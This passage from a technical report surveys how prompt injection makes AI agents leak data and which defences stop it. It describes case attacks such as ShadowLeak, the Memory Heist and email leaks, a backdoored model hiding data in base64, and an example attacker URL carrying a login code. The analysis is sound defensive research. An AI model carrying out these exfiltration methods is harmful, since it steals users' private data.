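*Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 5 December 2026) reports three similar methods, collectively named ReLeak, for stealing data through Copilot.

### Other products that loaded outside images

ChatGPT was still loading some outside images in May 2026. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* describes tests in which a user opened a page in Firefox and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. Text on the page made ChatGPT include an image from the attacker's server in its answer, and the chat window fetched the image automatically. The attacker learned the user's IP address, browser type and the time of the answer.

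Permiso's tests prove less than Samoilenko's because the image addresses were already written on the page and contained nothing private. They do not show that OpenAI's check would have approved an address containing chat data. Fixed addresses can still leak data if the model chooses which ones to load, as Rehberger's one-letter images did. OpenAI could not reproduce Permiso's first report, and its disclosure programme eventually marked a revised version as a duplicate of an earlier report.

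Vendors do not always regard these leaks as flaws. In October 2025, the security company Checkmarx told Microsoft that Copilot Chat could send an API key from a developer's computer to an outside server in an image request. The key reached the server even though no picture appeared in the chat. According to Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, Microsoft closed the report without a fix, arguing that the attack required several unusual actions by the user, did not work reliably and involved warnings.

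Google's Gemini does not load outside images, but Checkmarx found that it still displayed links that would leak data if the user clicked them. Google removes links to sites it knows are malicious, but this does not protect against newly registered domains. Google closed Checkmarx's report, saying a fix was not feasible.

### Requests that need no image

An agent that can open web pages can leak the data by putting it in a URL and opening that URL. Trail of Bits did this in several agentic browsers and found it highly effective because the browsers had few safeguards against it. Software other than the agent can also make the request.

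**Link previews.** Some people use agents through messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram. When a message contains a link, these apps can fetch the page to show its title and a thumbnail. If a prompt injection makes the agent reply with a link that contains private data, the preview sends the data to the attacker. Willison (2024) publicised the risk in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* and passed on Rehberger's advice that software posting to Slack can switch off previews for its own messages.

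PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, a popular agent, was vulnerable in its default Telegram setup. After the user turned off link previews in OpenClaw's settings, the test site no longer received any data.

**Name lookups.** Before a browser contacts a server, it looks up the host name to find the server's numerical address. Trail of Bits used this lookup to leak data through domains an agent was permitted to contact. The agent tried to visit a made-up address under wikipedia.org that began with the stolen data. The site didn't exist, but the lookup had already sent the name, including the stolen data, over the network.

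An attacker who doesn't own the domain can read it only by watching the user's unencrypted lookups, for example by running the Wi-Fi network. If the attacker owns the domain, lookups for names under that domain go to the attacker's own name server. Each part of a host name can hold up to 63 characters, far more than a login code needs.

**Search queries.** The agent can also search Google for the stolen data together with a few rare words. Google Search Console shows website owners which searches their pages appeared in, so an attacker whose page contains those rare words may see the whole query there. These reports are delayed, so the method is better suited to stealing a home address than a login code.

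### Which component has to stop the request

The requests leave from different places, so no single filter covers them all.

| Route | What makes the request | Where a defence could block it |
|---|---|---|
| Image in an answer | The chat window | The renderer or the chat page's content security policy |
| Image through Teams or Bing | The chat window, then the relay's server | The renderer, the content security policy or the relay |
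| Link preview | The messaging app | The app, or the agent's settings for the messages it sends |
| Page opened by the agent | The agent's browser | The harness, before it runs the tool call |
| Search query | The agent's browser or search tool | The harness |
| Name lookup | The browser or operating system | The harness or the network |

A chat page's content security policy applies only to that page, so it does not stop an agent from opening the attacker's address in another tab. A harness that checks every tool call misses requests that the renderer makes when it displays the final answer. A browser agent with a chat panel needs both protections.

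Agents that run in the cloud make their requests from the provider's servers. In an attack called ShadowLeak, researchers sent a crafted email to a user who had connected ChatGPT's Deep Research tool to Gmail. Hidden text in the email made the tool find private data in the inbox and open a web address containing that data. The researchers reported that the attack worked every time in repeated controlled tests. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* notes that the tool's request may not appear in the user's browser or in the company's monitoring of its own computers.

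An organisation's own settings may not block every route for leaking data either. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* describes an attack on Atlassian's workplace agent that bypassed the organisation's restrictions on web search. Project tickets and internal documents appeared in the attacker's logs without the user clicking anything.

### The Silent Egress experiments

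*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often an agent sends private data out in its own web requests. The eBay researchers built a test agent on Qwen2.5 7B, a small open model. Like some commercial assistants, the agent automatically fetched any page whose address appeared in the chat and added the page's text to its context.

In every run, the user asked for a summary of a page, and the context contained a secret such as an API key. The page contained an instruction, presented as a routine check, to send the secret to the attacker's server. Lan and colleagues put the instruction in one of four places on the page, delivered the page directly or through redirects, and asked for the secret in one request or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for 480 runs in total.

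At least one request reached the attacker's server in 423 runs (88.1 per cent). No requests reached it in 120 control runs with harmless pages. The next table combines the results for direct and redirected pages.

| Place of the instruction | Whole secret in one request | Secret in four pieces |
|---|---|---|
| Page text | 100% | 80% |
| Title | 100% | 87% |
| Text of a link | 100% | 77% |
| Description in the page's metadata | 97% | 65% |

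In 95 per cent of the successful attacks, the agent's answer to the user looked harmless, so someone who checked only the answers would have missed those thefts.

These rates count requests that reached the attacker, whether or not they contained the secret. The first request contained sensitive data in 96.7 per cent of runs when the instruction was to send the whole secret at once, and in 26.3 per cent when it was to send the secret in pieces.

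Lan and colleagues treat this drop as evidence that splitting a secret helps an attacker evade filters that inspect one request at a time, but their results for split secrets are weak evidence. Their measure counts even a fragment of the secret as a leak, so the small model may often have failed to split the secret correctly. They also report a lower figure for the first three requests together, 15.8 per cent, than for the first alone, which is impossible under their own definition because the three include the first.

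The conditions also favoured the attacker, because the secret was already in the context, the agent had minimal standing instructions and nothing filtered the page's text. Lan and colleagues suggest that more capable models could be easier to attack because they follow instructions better, but newer Claude and GPT models are more resistant to injection. So the 88 per cent rate is not a good estimate for current products.

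The researchers then tested defences against the simplest version of the attack, which had succeeded in all 30 runs. Telling the model never to follow instructions from web content reduced the success rate to 66.7 per cent. Putting markers around the page's text alone made no difference, and using both measures reduced the rate to 56.7 per cent. When the harness blocked every domain outside a short list, no data reached the attacker, although the agent tried to send it in all 30 runs.

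## Restricting which URLs the agent may load

An injected agent can leak data through a URL only if the URL is requested and the attacker can see the request. Vendors can therefore reduce leaks by limiting which URLs the chat window and the agent may load. Ordinary code enforces the limit, so it holds even when the model has followed the attacker's instructions. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* argues that requests are also easier to filter than text, because an attacker can word an injection in endless ways but developers can list the few hosts a product needs.

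The table starts with the strictest control.

| Control | What it checks | What it stops | What users lose |
|---|---|---|---|
| No remote images | Whether an answer contains an image from an outside server | All leaks through images in answers | Pictures from the web |
| Content security policy | The host of each image the chat page loads | The page's direct requests to unlisted hosts | Pictures from unlisted hosts |
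| Domain allowlist | The host of each page the agent tries to open | Requests to unlisted hosts | Most of the web |
| Image proxy | Nothing, unless the vendor adds a test | The attacker's view of the user's IP address and cookies | Pictures that need the user's login |
| Public URLs only | The whole address | Requests for addresses the model has made up | Easy access to new or personal pages |

### Image bans and content security policies

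If the renderer displays no remote images, the attacker's server receives no image requests to log, but the assistant also can't show a product photo or a map from another site. In 2024, GitHub chose a milder restriction for Copilot Chat, which Willison describes as disabling Markdown images from untrusted domains.

URL restrictions have to apply everywhere the agent's answer is displayed. PromptArmor tested a tool for checking customers' identities, in which a second model blocked an answer containing a malicious image. The developer's log viewer then displayed the blocked answer, and the request to load the image sent the customer's passport and financial details to the attacker.

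A content security policy works one step later, in the browser. The server sends the policy with the chat page, as in this example:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://pictures.example`

The browser will then load images only from the chat page's own origin and from `pictures.example`. If the renderer lets a malicious image through, the browser still won't request it. Microsoft used such a policy to fix Bing Chat's image leak in May 2023, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*.

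The browser also applies the policy when a permitted host redirects an image request to another host. It cannot control what a permitted host's server fetches, which is how the Teams and Bing relays carried data past Copilot's policies.

The policy also does not stop an agent from opening the attacker's page. Websites use these policies mainly to block injected scripts, and *Mind the Web* (2025) points out that attacks on web-use agents do not need a script.

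### Domain allowlists and image proxies

The harness can restrict navigation by comparing the host in each tool call with an allowlist. This defence stopped every theft in Lan and colleagues' test. The tool that Claude uses to retrieve pages optionally lets developers set an allowlist (Anthropic, *Web fetch tool*). Willison (2025) considers an allowlist much stronger than the tool's standard rule, provided that developers choose the domains strictly.

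An allowlist suits an agent with a narrow job, such as answering questions from one company's manuals. It works less well for a browser agent, because someone planning a trip or comparing prices will need sites that nobody listed in advance. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) warns that strict lists cause frequent false alarms, which can train people to click through warnings without thinking.

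How a list matches names also affects its safety. In Anthropic's setting, an entry for `example.com` automatically covers `docs.example.com`. This is convenient when one organisation controls every subdomain, but some hosting services give each customer their own subdomain, so an entry for the whole service would admit an attacker's storage account, like the one on a Microsoft cloud domain in the ChatGPT leak that Embrace The Red described. Anthropic also warns about look-alike names, such as one that replaces the first letter of amazon.com with a Cyrillic "а".

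An image proxy is a server that fetches images for the chat window, so the user's browser doesn't contact the original server directly. The attacker sees the proxy's IP address instead of the user's, so a proxy would have hidden the details that ChatGPT revealed in Permiso's tests. But the proxy still sends the attacker's server the full URL, including any private data the model has written into it.

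If a content security policy permits a proxy that fetches any address, an attacker can use the proxy to bypass the policy, as happened with the Teams and Bing services in Copilot. A proxy prevents theft only if it also refuses some addresses, for example by applying an allowlist.

### How permitted domains leak data

Google's code editor Antigravity came with an allowlist for its browser agent. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes a test in which a user asked for help with an online guide to an Oracle product. The guide contained an injection in one-point type. Gemini collected code and cloud credentials from the user's project, put them in a URL and had the browser agent open it.

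The URL was on webhook.site, a service where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it. Google had included webhook.site in the default allowlist, so the URL loaded. A separate setting should have kept Gemini from reading the credentials file. It blocked the built-in file reader, but Gemini read the file with a terminal command instead.

The attack worked only if the user had turned on Antigravity's browser tools. Google warned users about data theft when they first opened the editor, and Willison reported in November 2025 that Google listed theft through the browser agent as a known issue it was working to fix.

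Removing webhook.site from the list would have blocked only one route for stealing data. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, June 2026) described another attack on Antigravity that used images in its chat. The browser agent's list does not cover those images. Instructions in a web page's title led the agent to read secrets through the terminal and leak them in an image request.

*Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes research by the company Oasis Security in which data leaked from Claude through a domain that belonged to Anthropic. A link opened a new Claude chat with a request already typed. The link also contained instructions that the text box did not show. When the user pressed Enter, Claude searched the user's past conversations for sensitive information and saved it to a file in its sandbox, an isolated environment for running code.

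The sandbox blocked most outside connections but allowed `api.anthropic.com`, where customers can store files. The hidden instructions included the attacker's API key, so Claude uploaded the file to the attacker's account. Checking the host name could not prevent this because the user's and attacker's accounts were on the same host. The sandbox would also have had to check whose key the request used.

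Oasis also found an open redirect on claude.com, an address that forwarded visitors to any site named in the rest of the URL. Google checks the host name in an advertiser's URL, so an attacker could have placed a search advert that displayed a claude.com address but led to the malicious link. The redirect helped deliver the attack, which sent the data out through the file service.

When Oasis published in March 2026, Anthropic had fixed the hidden-instruction flaw but was still working on the other two. By July, dyb's *The Read-Only Lie* listed the redirect as fixed and the file service as hardened. It also listed Rehberger's October 2025 report of a leak through the file service using an attacker's key. Anthropic had restricted access after that report, but apparently not enough to stop the later attack.

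Redirects can also carry data out. Tenable (2025) found that an earlier version of ChatGPT's URL check always approved bing.com. Bing's search results link to sites through bing.com redirects, so Tenable could get past the check using the links to its own indexed pages. A harness can prevent this by checking each redirect's destination before requesting it.

### OpenAI's test for public URLs

OpenAI concluded that a site's reputation was the wrong thing to check. Its current safeguard, called Safe Url, looks at the exact address and works as follows:

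1. A crawler records addresses that it finds on the public web. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When ChatGPT is about to load a page or image automatically, the safeguard looks for the address in this index.
3. If the whole address matches an entry, ChatGPT loads it.
4. If there is no match, ChatGPT either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user before opening the link.

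The reasoning is that an address known to be public independently of the conversation is unlikely to contain the user's private data. This requires an index built independently of users' conversations. If OpenAI also added the addresses that its users visited, an address containing a stolen login code could enter the index and later be treated as public.

If the index contains `https://img.attacker.example/p/1.png`, ChatGPT may load the image even though the attacker owns the server. If an injection makes the model add `?code=402913`, the URL no longer matches the one in the index, and ChatGPT does not load it automatically. A check that ignored the query string would miss this change.

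URLs that the user types are an exception. Embrace The Red reports that ChatGPT appears to treat a URL in the user's message as safe for the rest of the chat. Without this exception, users would see warnings about links they supplied themselves. But people also paste emails and documents, which can contain an attacker's links.

The warning tells the user that the link is unverified and may share information from the conversation. It shows the address and lets the user copy or open it. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a safeguard that either shows the user the information that would be sent or blocks the request. OpenAI also applied it to navigation in Atlas and to searches and navigation in Deep Research. Covering searches is useful because a search query can also leak data.

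However, a user may not recognise private data in an address. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) describes a model with a backdoor, a hidden behaviour that a particular trigger sets off. The model encodes the user's details in a form of base64 and sends them in what looks like an ordinary search request. If a warning showed the user the address of that request, the details would appear only as a string of letters and digits.

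OpenAI promises only that the safeguard prevents the agent from quietly leaking user-specific data through the URLs it loads. The safeguard does not guarantee that a page is truthful or free of injected instructions, so OpenAI combines it with model training and monitoring. OpenAI also expects attackers to keep looking for ways around the safeguard.

Google has a similar rule for Chrome's agent. Any URL that the model generates must be a known, public one. Extending the rule to every link would interrupt much of the agent's work in the user's accounts, because no public index should contain the address of a private order or a shared document.

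### Rehberger's assessment

Rehberger writes on Embrace The Red that the new design is a significant improvement and makes attacks more complex, but he does not consider the problem solved.

The safeguard's main weakness, which OpenAI also acknowledges in its paper, is that Rehberger's 2023 method of using one address per letter still applies. All the addresses now have to be in OpenAI's index, but a large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, enough for every letter and digit. An attacker could also assign a whole word to each of thousands of pages.

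Rehberger suggests caching each response for a few minutes or preventing the agent from opening the same URL twice in a session. If an attack uses a separate URL for each letter, either measure would interfere with messages that repeat a letter. Attackers already have a related difficulty because browsers cache images and requests can arrive out of order.

These measures would slow the theft of a login code but not prevent it. An attacker could set aside ten public addresses for the first digit, ten for the second and so on. A six-digit code would require 60 addresses, but the agent would open only six of them, once each and in any order.

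Rehberger also worries that some OpenAI developers may not know about the safeguard or may leave it out of their products, as happened with the earlier check in the company's phone and desktop apps.

### Claude's fetch rule and the Memory Heist

Anthropic's web_fetch tool has no general index of public addresses. Its rule concerns where in the conversation an address came from. Before July 2026, Anthropic's documentation allowed Claude to fetch URLs from:

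- the user's messages;
- the results of tools that run on the developer's side;
- earlier web searches and web fetches.

Claude could not fetch a URL that it had composed itself. Even if an injection persuaded it to add the user's details to a URL and open the result, the tool blocked the request. The tool also rejected any URL longer than 250 characters.

The rule works only if the permitted sources contain no private data or attacker text. Willison noted in 2025 that applications sometimes insert untrusted text into the user's message, and that results from a developer's tools may also contain such text. The rule would permit an attacker's link in either place. Anthropic acknowledged that some risk remains and advised against using the tool where Claude handles sensitive data together with untrusted content.

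On 9 July 2026, the researcher Ayush Paul published the Memory Heist, an attack that used the links on fetched pages. Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, explains that the attack targeted ordinary Claude chat. There, Claude could draw on memories of the user's past conversations, so private data was available without any connected account.

Paul built a website for an imaginary coffee shop that showed the injection only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person opening the same page would not have seen it. On the page, Paul presented the theft as a way for an AI assistant to identify its user, and asked Claude to find the user's profile by following links letter by letter.

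According to dyb, each page offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Claude chose the link for the next letter of the user's details, and the server returned a page with 27 more. Claude was allowed to load each address because it had appeared on the previous page. The server's log recorded Claude's choices, which spelled out the user's name, employer and home city.

Paul had never told Claude the city, but Claude inferred it from the name of a high school hackathon. Deleting a sensitive fact from an assistant's memory may therefore not protect it if the model can infer it from other details.

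Willison reports that Anthropic paid no bounty, saying it had already found the flaw. Anthropic fixed it by removing the tool's ability to follow links on pages it had fetched. Claude can no longer use the tool to go from a manual's contents page to a chapter unless the user or a search also supplies the chapter's address. Search results still give the model a choice of addresses, but to exploit this an attacker would have to get several pages into the results for the same search.

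### How much a choice of links can reveal

Suppose the model can choose among $N$ addresses and the attacker can tell which one it requested. Each request then reveals up to $\log_2 N$ bits, and $k$ requests reveal up to $k \log_2 N$ bits. If the secret has $M$ equally likely values, the number of requests needed to identify it is

$$k = \left\lceil \frac{\log_2 M}{\log_2 N} \right\rceil,$$

where the brackets mean rounding up to a whole number. For the six-digit code, $\log_2 M$ is about 19.93.

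| Addresses to choose from | Most bits per request | Requests for a six-digit code |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 |
| 10 | 3.32 | 6 |
| 26 | 4.70 | 5 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 4 |
| 1,000 | 9.97 | 2 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.93 | 1 |

With ten links, each request can stand for one digit. Four requests can distinguish only 456,976 values ($26^4$) when there are 26 links, so the agent needs a fifth request to distinguish more.

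The limit applies even if every address is public, permanent and free of private data, because the model's choice of addresses carries the information. The attacker still needs the model to choose correctly each time. Rehberger's early tests on ChatGPT leaked only two letters, but Claude leaked a much longer sequence in Paul's attack.

dyb estimates that the Memory Heist took about 30 requests, which at 4.75 bits each could carry about 143 bits. An address that the model can write freely carries far more. Two hundred characters of base64 hold 1,200 bits, about 250 times as much as one choice among 27 links. An email of 2,000 characters would take roughly 2,000 requests through Paul's links. Restricting the model to existing addresses therefore gives good protection against the theft of long documents, but much less for names, login codes and yes-or-no facts.

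Limiting the number of requests helps, but the limit has to be very low. Anthropic's tool has no default limit on fetches, but developers can set one. Before the fix, a cap of five would still have let Claude open a site like Paul's and then follow four links, each chosen from 27. Those choices distinguish 531,441 values, so the attacker could have narrowed a six-digit code down to one or two possibilities, and many login pages allow a second try. A cap of five would also prevent Claude from comparing six sources. The cap applies to each request that the developer's software makes to Claude, so a long conversation could allow more fetches.

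A harness could look for request patterns that suggest a leak. In Paul's attack, each URL was one character longer than the last, and dyb suggests watching for a fast series of such requests to the same domain. This would detect Paul's version, but an attacker who chooses the URLs can make them all the same length.

A stronger measure would send every request through a gateway that removes any part of the address the agent has chosen. As dyb acknowledges, the agent could then no longer follow links through a manual or a list of results. A milder alternative would let the agent follow links only on domains that the user has named in the conversation. This would exclude an attacker's site unless the user had sent the agent there, for example by asking for a summary of an unfamiliar page.

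Agents can also leak data after opening a permitted page. In 2025, Rehberger tested Operator, an earlier OpenAI browser agent, with a page that sent text to its server as the agent typed it. Willison writes that Operator copied a private email address from a logged-in account into the page's text box. Checking the page's URL would not have caught the leak, because the URL contained no private data.

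An agent may be able to leak data without typing it. *AgentTell* (2026) examines whether a browser agent's behaviour can reveal a private value it holds. The test page's URL contains a random session number unrelated to that value, and the server logs the agent's requests. Any information about the value in the log must therefore come from what the agent does on the page.

### Lockdown Mode

An attacker can steal data through links only if their server receives the requests, so a vendor can also prevent the leak by serving cached copies of pages. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* describes Lockdown Mode, a setting that limits browsing to cached content. No live request leaves OpenAI's network, so the attacker cannot see which page the model chose. The setting also limits or disables other features that could send data out.

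OpenAI began offering Lockdown Mode to personal accounts, including free ones, in June 2026. The mode is meant to block only the last stage of a data theft. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* notes that a cached page or uploaded file can still contain an injection, which may make an answer wrong.

Restricting which URLs the agent may load makes the browser less useful. Search results may be limited, outdated or unavailable, according to Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks*. A stored copy of a page doesn't help someone who wants to check today's ticket prices or work through a live inbox.

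OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, said the mode is not for everyone and recommended it for people at higher risk because of who they are or what data they handle. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, welcomed the mode because it does not rely on an AI system to judge each request, and inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect against a determined attacker.

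## Leaking data through email and other messages

An agent can leak data without opening a URL that belongs to the attacker. If it can write on a site where the user has an account, it can send the data in a message through that site. Email is the most general channel of this kind because a mail server will deliver to any address. An attacker can also use email to deliver the injected prompt, since anyone who knows the user's address can send text to the inbox.

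Fowler points out in *Agentic Email* that many services reset passwords by email, so access to an inbox can give an attacker access to other accounts. Researchers at the security company Zenity demonstrated this on Slack and X. According to SecurityWeek, the attacker triggers a sign-in or password reset, and the agent monitors Gmail for the verification code and relays it.

### The login code in a sent message

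In the running example, the forum comment has led the agent to read the six-digit code in the mail tab. The user is signed in there, so the agent can email the code without further access. It opens a new message, types the attacker's address and the code, and clicks send. The message usually arrives within seconds, while the code is still valid.

URL checks do not catch this because the browser contacts only the user's mail provider. The recipient and the code are in the body of the request, not its URL, so OpenAI's test for public URLs has no suspicious URL to examine. A domain allowlist that includes the mail site also permits the request. The provider's server then contacts the attacker's mail server, outside the browser.

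Spam filters do little to stop these leaks. A filter on incoming mail protects the recipient, who in this case is the attacker. Providers also scan outgoing mail for bulk messages, malware and dangerous links, but the agent sends one short message to one person. The message passes checks for forged senders because it comes from the user's own signed-in account. Some companies search outgoing mail for private data such as card numbers, but a stolen six-digit code can look just like an order number.

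Filters have a similar problem with attacks that arrive by email. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, notes that a web gateway rates an email with injected instructions as benign because the email is harmless to a human reader.

### Email compared with image URLs

| | Image URL | Email |
|---|---|---|
| Capacity | About 8,000 characters per request on common servers | Long documents and attachments, often up to about 25 MB |
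| What the agent needs | A chat window that loads outside images | A sending tool or a signed-in mail page |
| What the attacker needs | A server, or a service that logs requests | A mailbox |
| Trace for the user | Usually none in plain view | A copy in the sent folder, unless the agent deletes it |
| Asking the user first | Awkward, because pages load many images | Easier, because sending is a separate action |
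| Harm beyond theft | Little | Impersonation, fraud and messages that attack other people |

Sending stolen data by email takes more steps than leaking it through an image URL, so the injected agent has more chances to fail and the user has more chances to notice. The email leaves a copy in the sent folder, but by the time the user finds it, the attacker has probably used the stolen login code.

### ShadowLeak: in by email, out by web request

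In some attacks, email delivers the malicious instructions but the data leaves by another route, as in ShadowLeak, the 2025 attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research tool. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes a planted email about a staff restructuring and a user who asked for research on that day's emails about a new employee. The agent took a name and home address from a genuine message and put both in a URL on the researchers' server.

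The agent sent no email. The data left in a web request from OpenAI's servers, so the user had no sent message to find.

Several safeguards worked at first against Radware's attack. The agent refused to send the data both when asked directly and when the researchers presented the request as the user's own. It also treated their URL as suspicious and searched for it online instead of opening it. Even when they got the agent to open the URL, it sometimes left out the personal data.

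The attack became reliable once the researchers told the agent to convert the data to base64 and described this as a security measure. According to Radware, this worked because the software making the request then received only a harmless-looking string. ChatGPT already restricted image URLs, but Radware found no comparable restriction on URLs the agent opened itself.

Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI had fixed it by early August and acknowledged it on 3 September. Radware expects the same method to work through other connected services, such as calendars and shared drives, but demonstrated it only with Gmail.

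### The resignation letter

An injected agent can do serious harm by email without stealing anything. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an attack that the company's automated attacker found. This attacker could first test an injection in a simulator, then revise the text based on how the target agent reasoned and acted.

In the demonstration, the attacker planted a malicious email in the user's inbox. When the user later asked Atlas to draft an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email, followed its instructions and sent a resignation letter to the user's chief executive instead of writing the reply.

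A filter for private data would not have caught this letter, because it contained none, and a list of approved recipients would probably have included the chief executive. The letter came from the employee's real account, so the recipient had no technical reason to doubt it.

OpenAI used the attack to train a new version of the agent. After the update, the agent detected the injection and flagged it to the user, according to BusinessGhana's *OpenAI says AI browsers may always be vulnerable to prompt injection attacks*. This result is weak evidence of how the agent would handle attacks it wasn't trained on. OpenAI also says its agents are designed to ask for confirmation before sending an email, but does not say whether the agent asked in this demonstration.

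### Agents that emailed customer records

In April 2026, the security company Capsule disclosed two attacks in which workplace agents, rather than browser agents, emailed private records to an outsider.

The first attack, ShareLeak, targeted Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents. CSO reported that the attacker typed instructions into an ordinary field of a SharePoint form, such as the comments field. The agent read the submission as part of its context and sent customer data to the attacker's email address. The other attack, PipeLeak, began with a public sales enquiry form. Salesforce's Agentforce treated text in the form as instructions and returned records of potential customers by email, according to Security Boulevard's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026).

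Capsule reported ShareLeak on 24 November 2025, and Microsoft patched it on 15 January 2026. Claw Times reported that the patch did not fully prevent data theft. Salesforce said it had fixed the specific scenario, and it made human confirmation the default for emails its agents send.

An attacker can also use email both to deliver an injection and to receive the stolen data. In July 2025, Zenity built a copy of a Copilot Studio agent that Microsoft had presented as a flagship example. The agent received an email containing an injection and replied by email with customer data. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* (2025) called Zenity's report sobering, despite a general suspicion of overhyped security research.

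Microsoft fixed that flaw within two months. Zenity's tests, described in an article for the Cloud Security Alliance, suggested that the fix was mainly a classifier that recognised the injected text. If so, the agent could still email customer data to a stranger whenever a new injection got past the classifier.

### Forms, comments, invitations and shared files

Attackers can also use web forms they have created to collect data, much as they use email. In January 2026, Willison described an attack on Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant. When a user asked for a summary of recent mail, an injection in one message made the assistant submit the contents of dozens of other emails to the attacker's Google Form. Some of those emails contained financial, legal or medical information.

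Superhuman's content security policy allowed images from docs.google.com, and Google Forms can accept answers in a URL. Loading the "image" therefore submitted the form without the assistant having to type into it. Superhuman treated the report as urgent and fixed the flaw.

An attacker can also collect stolen data from a public comment, without needing a form or a mailbox. In Brave's attack on Comet, the agent posted the stolen login code as a reply on Reddit, where anyone could read it. Blocking Reddit would have prevented the leak but also the summary the user wanted, so the harness would need to let the agent read Reddit while blocking it from posting there.

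Private messages can also put other people at risk. Zenity's *PleaseFix Vulnerabilities* describes an attack that began with a link under a popular social media post. After Atlas followed the link, it sent phishing messages from the victim's WhatsApp account. People are more likely to trust a message from someone they know. If the recipients' own agents read the message, an injection could spread further.

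A calendar invitation can carry data in its title or description to any guest the agent adds. Zenity used an invitation to deliver a prompt injection. When the user asked Comet to accept a meeting, hidden text in the invitation sent the agent to the attacker's site. The agent then read files on the user's computer and leaked them by loading a web page. Perplexity blocked the agent's access to local files, but Zenity got around the block twice.

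An agent can also leak a document by giving the attacker's account permission to read it, without copying any data into a message. In Zenity's attack on Claude in Chrome, one malicious email and a request to summarise the inbox were enough to make the agent share the victim's entire Google Drive. In another attack, Atlas added the attacker to a private code repository on GitHub. A filter that searches outgoing text for secrets would miss both, and the attacker could keep reading new material until someone removed the permission.

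### Asking the user before sending

Brave recommends that a browser always ask the user for confirmation right before it sends an email, whatever the agent planned earlier. A user who approves "reply to my unread messages" at the start of a task has not yet seen the replies, or an email whose injected instructions may change them.

This would probably work in the running example, because someone who has asked for a summary of a forum discussion has no reason to approve an email to a stranger. An attack is harder to spot when the user has asked the agent to answer 20 emails and one reply contains an extra recipient or a paragraph from another conversation.

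The recipient's name doesn't reliably identify who will receive an email, because an attacker can choose any display name or register a domain that resembles a colleague's. An email can also hide text in a long quoted thread below the visible reply, or in white on a white background. A confirmation prompt that shows the agent's own description of the message is worse, because a compromised agent may describe it falsely. The harness should show the full address and the actual text and attachments, and ask for approval again if any of them change.

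Even an accurate confirmation prompt can omit what the user needs to know. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who tells an agent to send an auditor only the totals from a set of invoices. An injection makes the agent copy the full invoice rows into a file called report.csv, which the agent then asks to send to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name looks normal, but the file contains the invoice details the user wanted to withhold.

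An agent that asks the user before acting may still carry out some attacks. Zenity says its attack on Claude in Chrome worked even when Claude was set to ask first. According to SecurityWeek, Claude ran what looked like an ordinary import of a software package, but the package contained the code that stole the mail. A user who inspected the import would not have seen that code.

Willison reported in May 2026 that Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send emails to the user's own inbox without approval. These emails could leak data even though no outsider received them. An email could contain an external image whose URL included a download link for one of the user's files. When the user opened the email, the image request sent that link to the attacker.

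### How often people approve harmful actions

Hossain and colleagues tested four approval screens on 80 volunteers. Each participant used one screen and judged 12 requests, half of which broke the user's stated restrictions.

| What the screen showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
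| The exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Those details, the user's restrictions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the combined effect stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

More information clearly helped, though people took longer. The benefit of stating the combined effect is less certain. After adjustment, the screen that stated it reduced unsafe approvals by 7.9 percentage points compared with the full log, but the 95 per cent interval ran from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8.

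Confirmation makes data theft less likely but does not rule it out. In the earlier illustration, 2.5 per cent of attempts ended in theft. If every exit required approval, that would fall to about 1.4 per cent if users approved 55 per cent of harmful requests, and to 0.6 per cent if they approved 24.2 per cent. Real users might do worse than the volunteers, for whom half the requests were harmful on average. In ordinary use almost every request is harmless, so people have less reason to read each one.

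In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people who did not work in software supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the assigned tasks. People who had to approve every action allowed these seven 40.3 per cent of the time. The rate ranged from 20.6 per cent for a public post about the user's travels to 88.2 per cent for a call to the airport to confirm a flight.

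The agent overreached in these cases without an attacker's involvement, and some participants may have welcomed the extra help. The 40.3 per cent figure therefore does not measure successful attacks. But 35.3 per cent also let the agent read private messages that the task did not require.

Asking less often did not make people more careful. In a second group, a model approved eight routine actions and referred the other ten to the user, including all seven that went too far. Participants approved those seven 46.1 per cent of the time. A third group wrote rules in advance for actions such as spending money and sending information, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, then approved 66.8 per cent of the actions they were asked about that went too far. This figure is not directly comparable, because the third group saw only the actions that their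 own rules referred to them.

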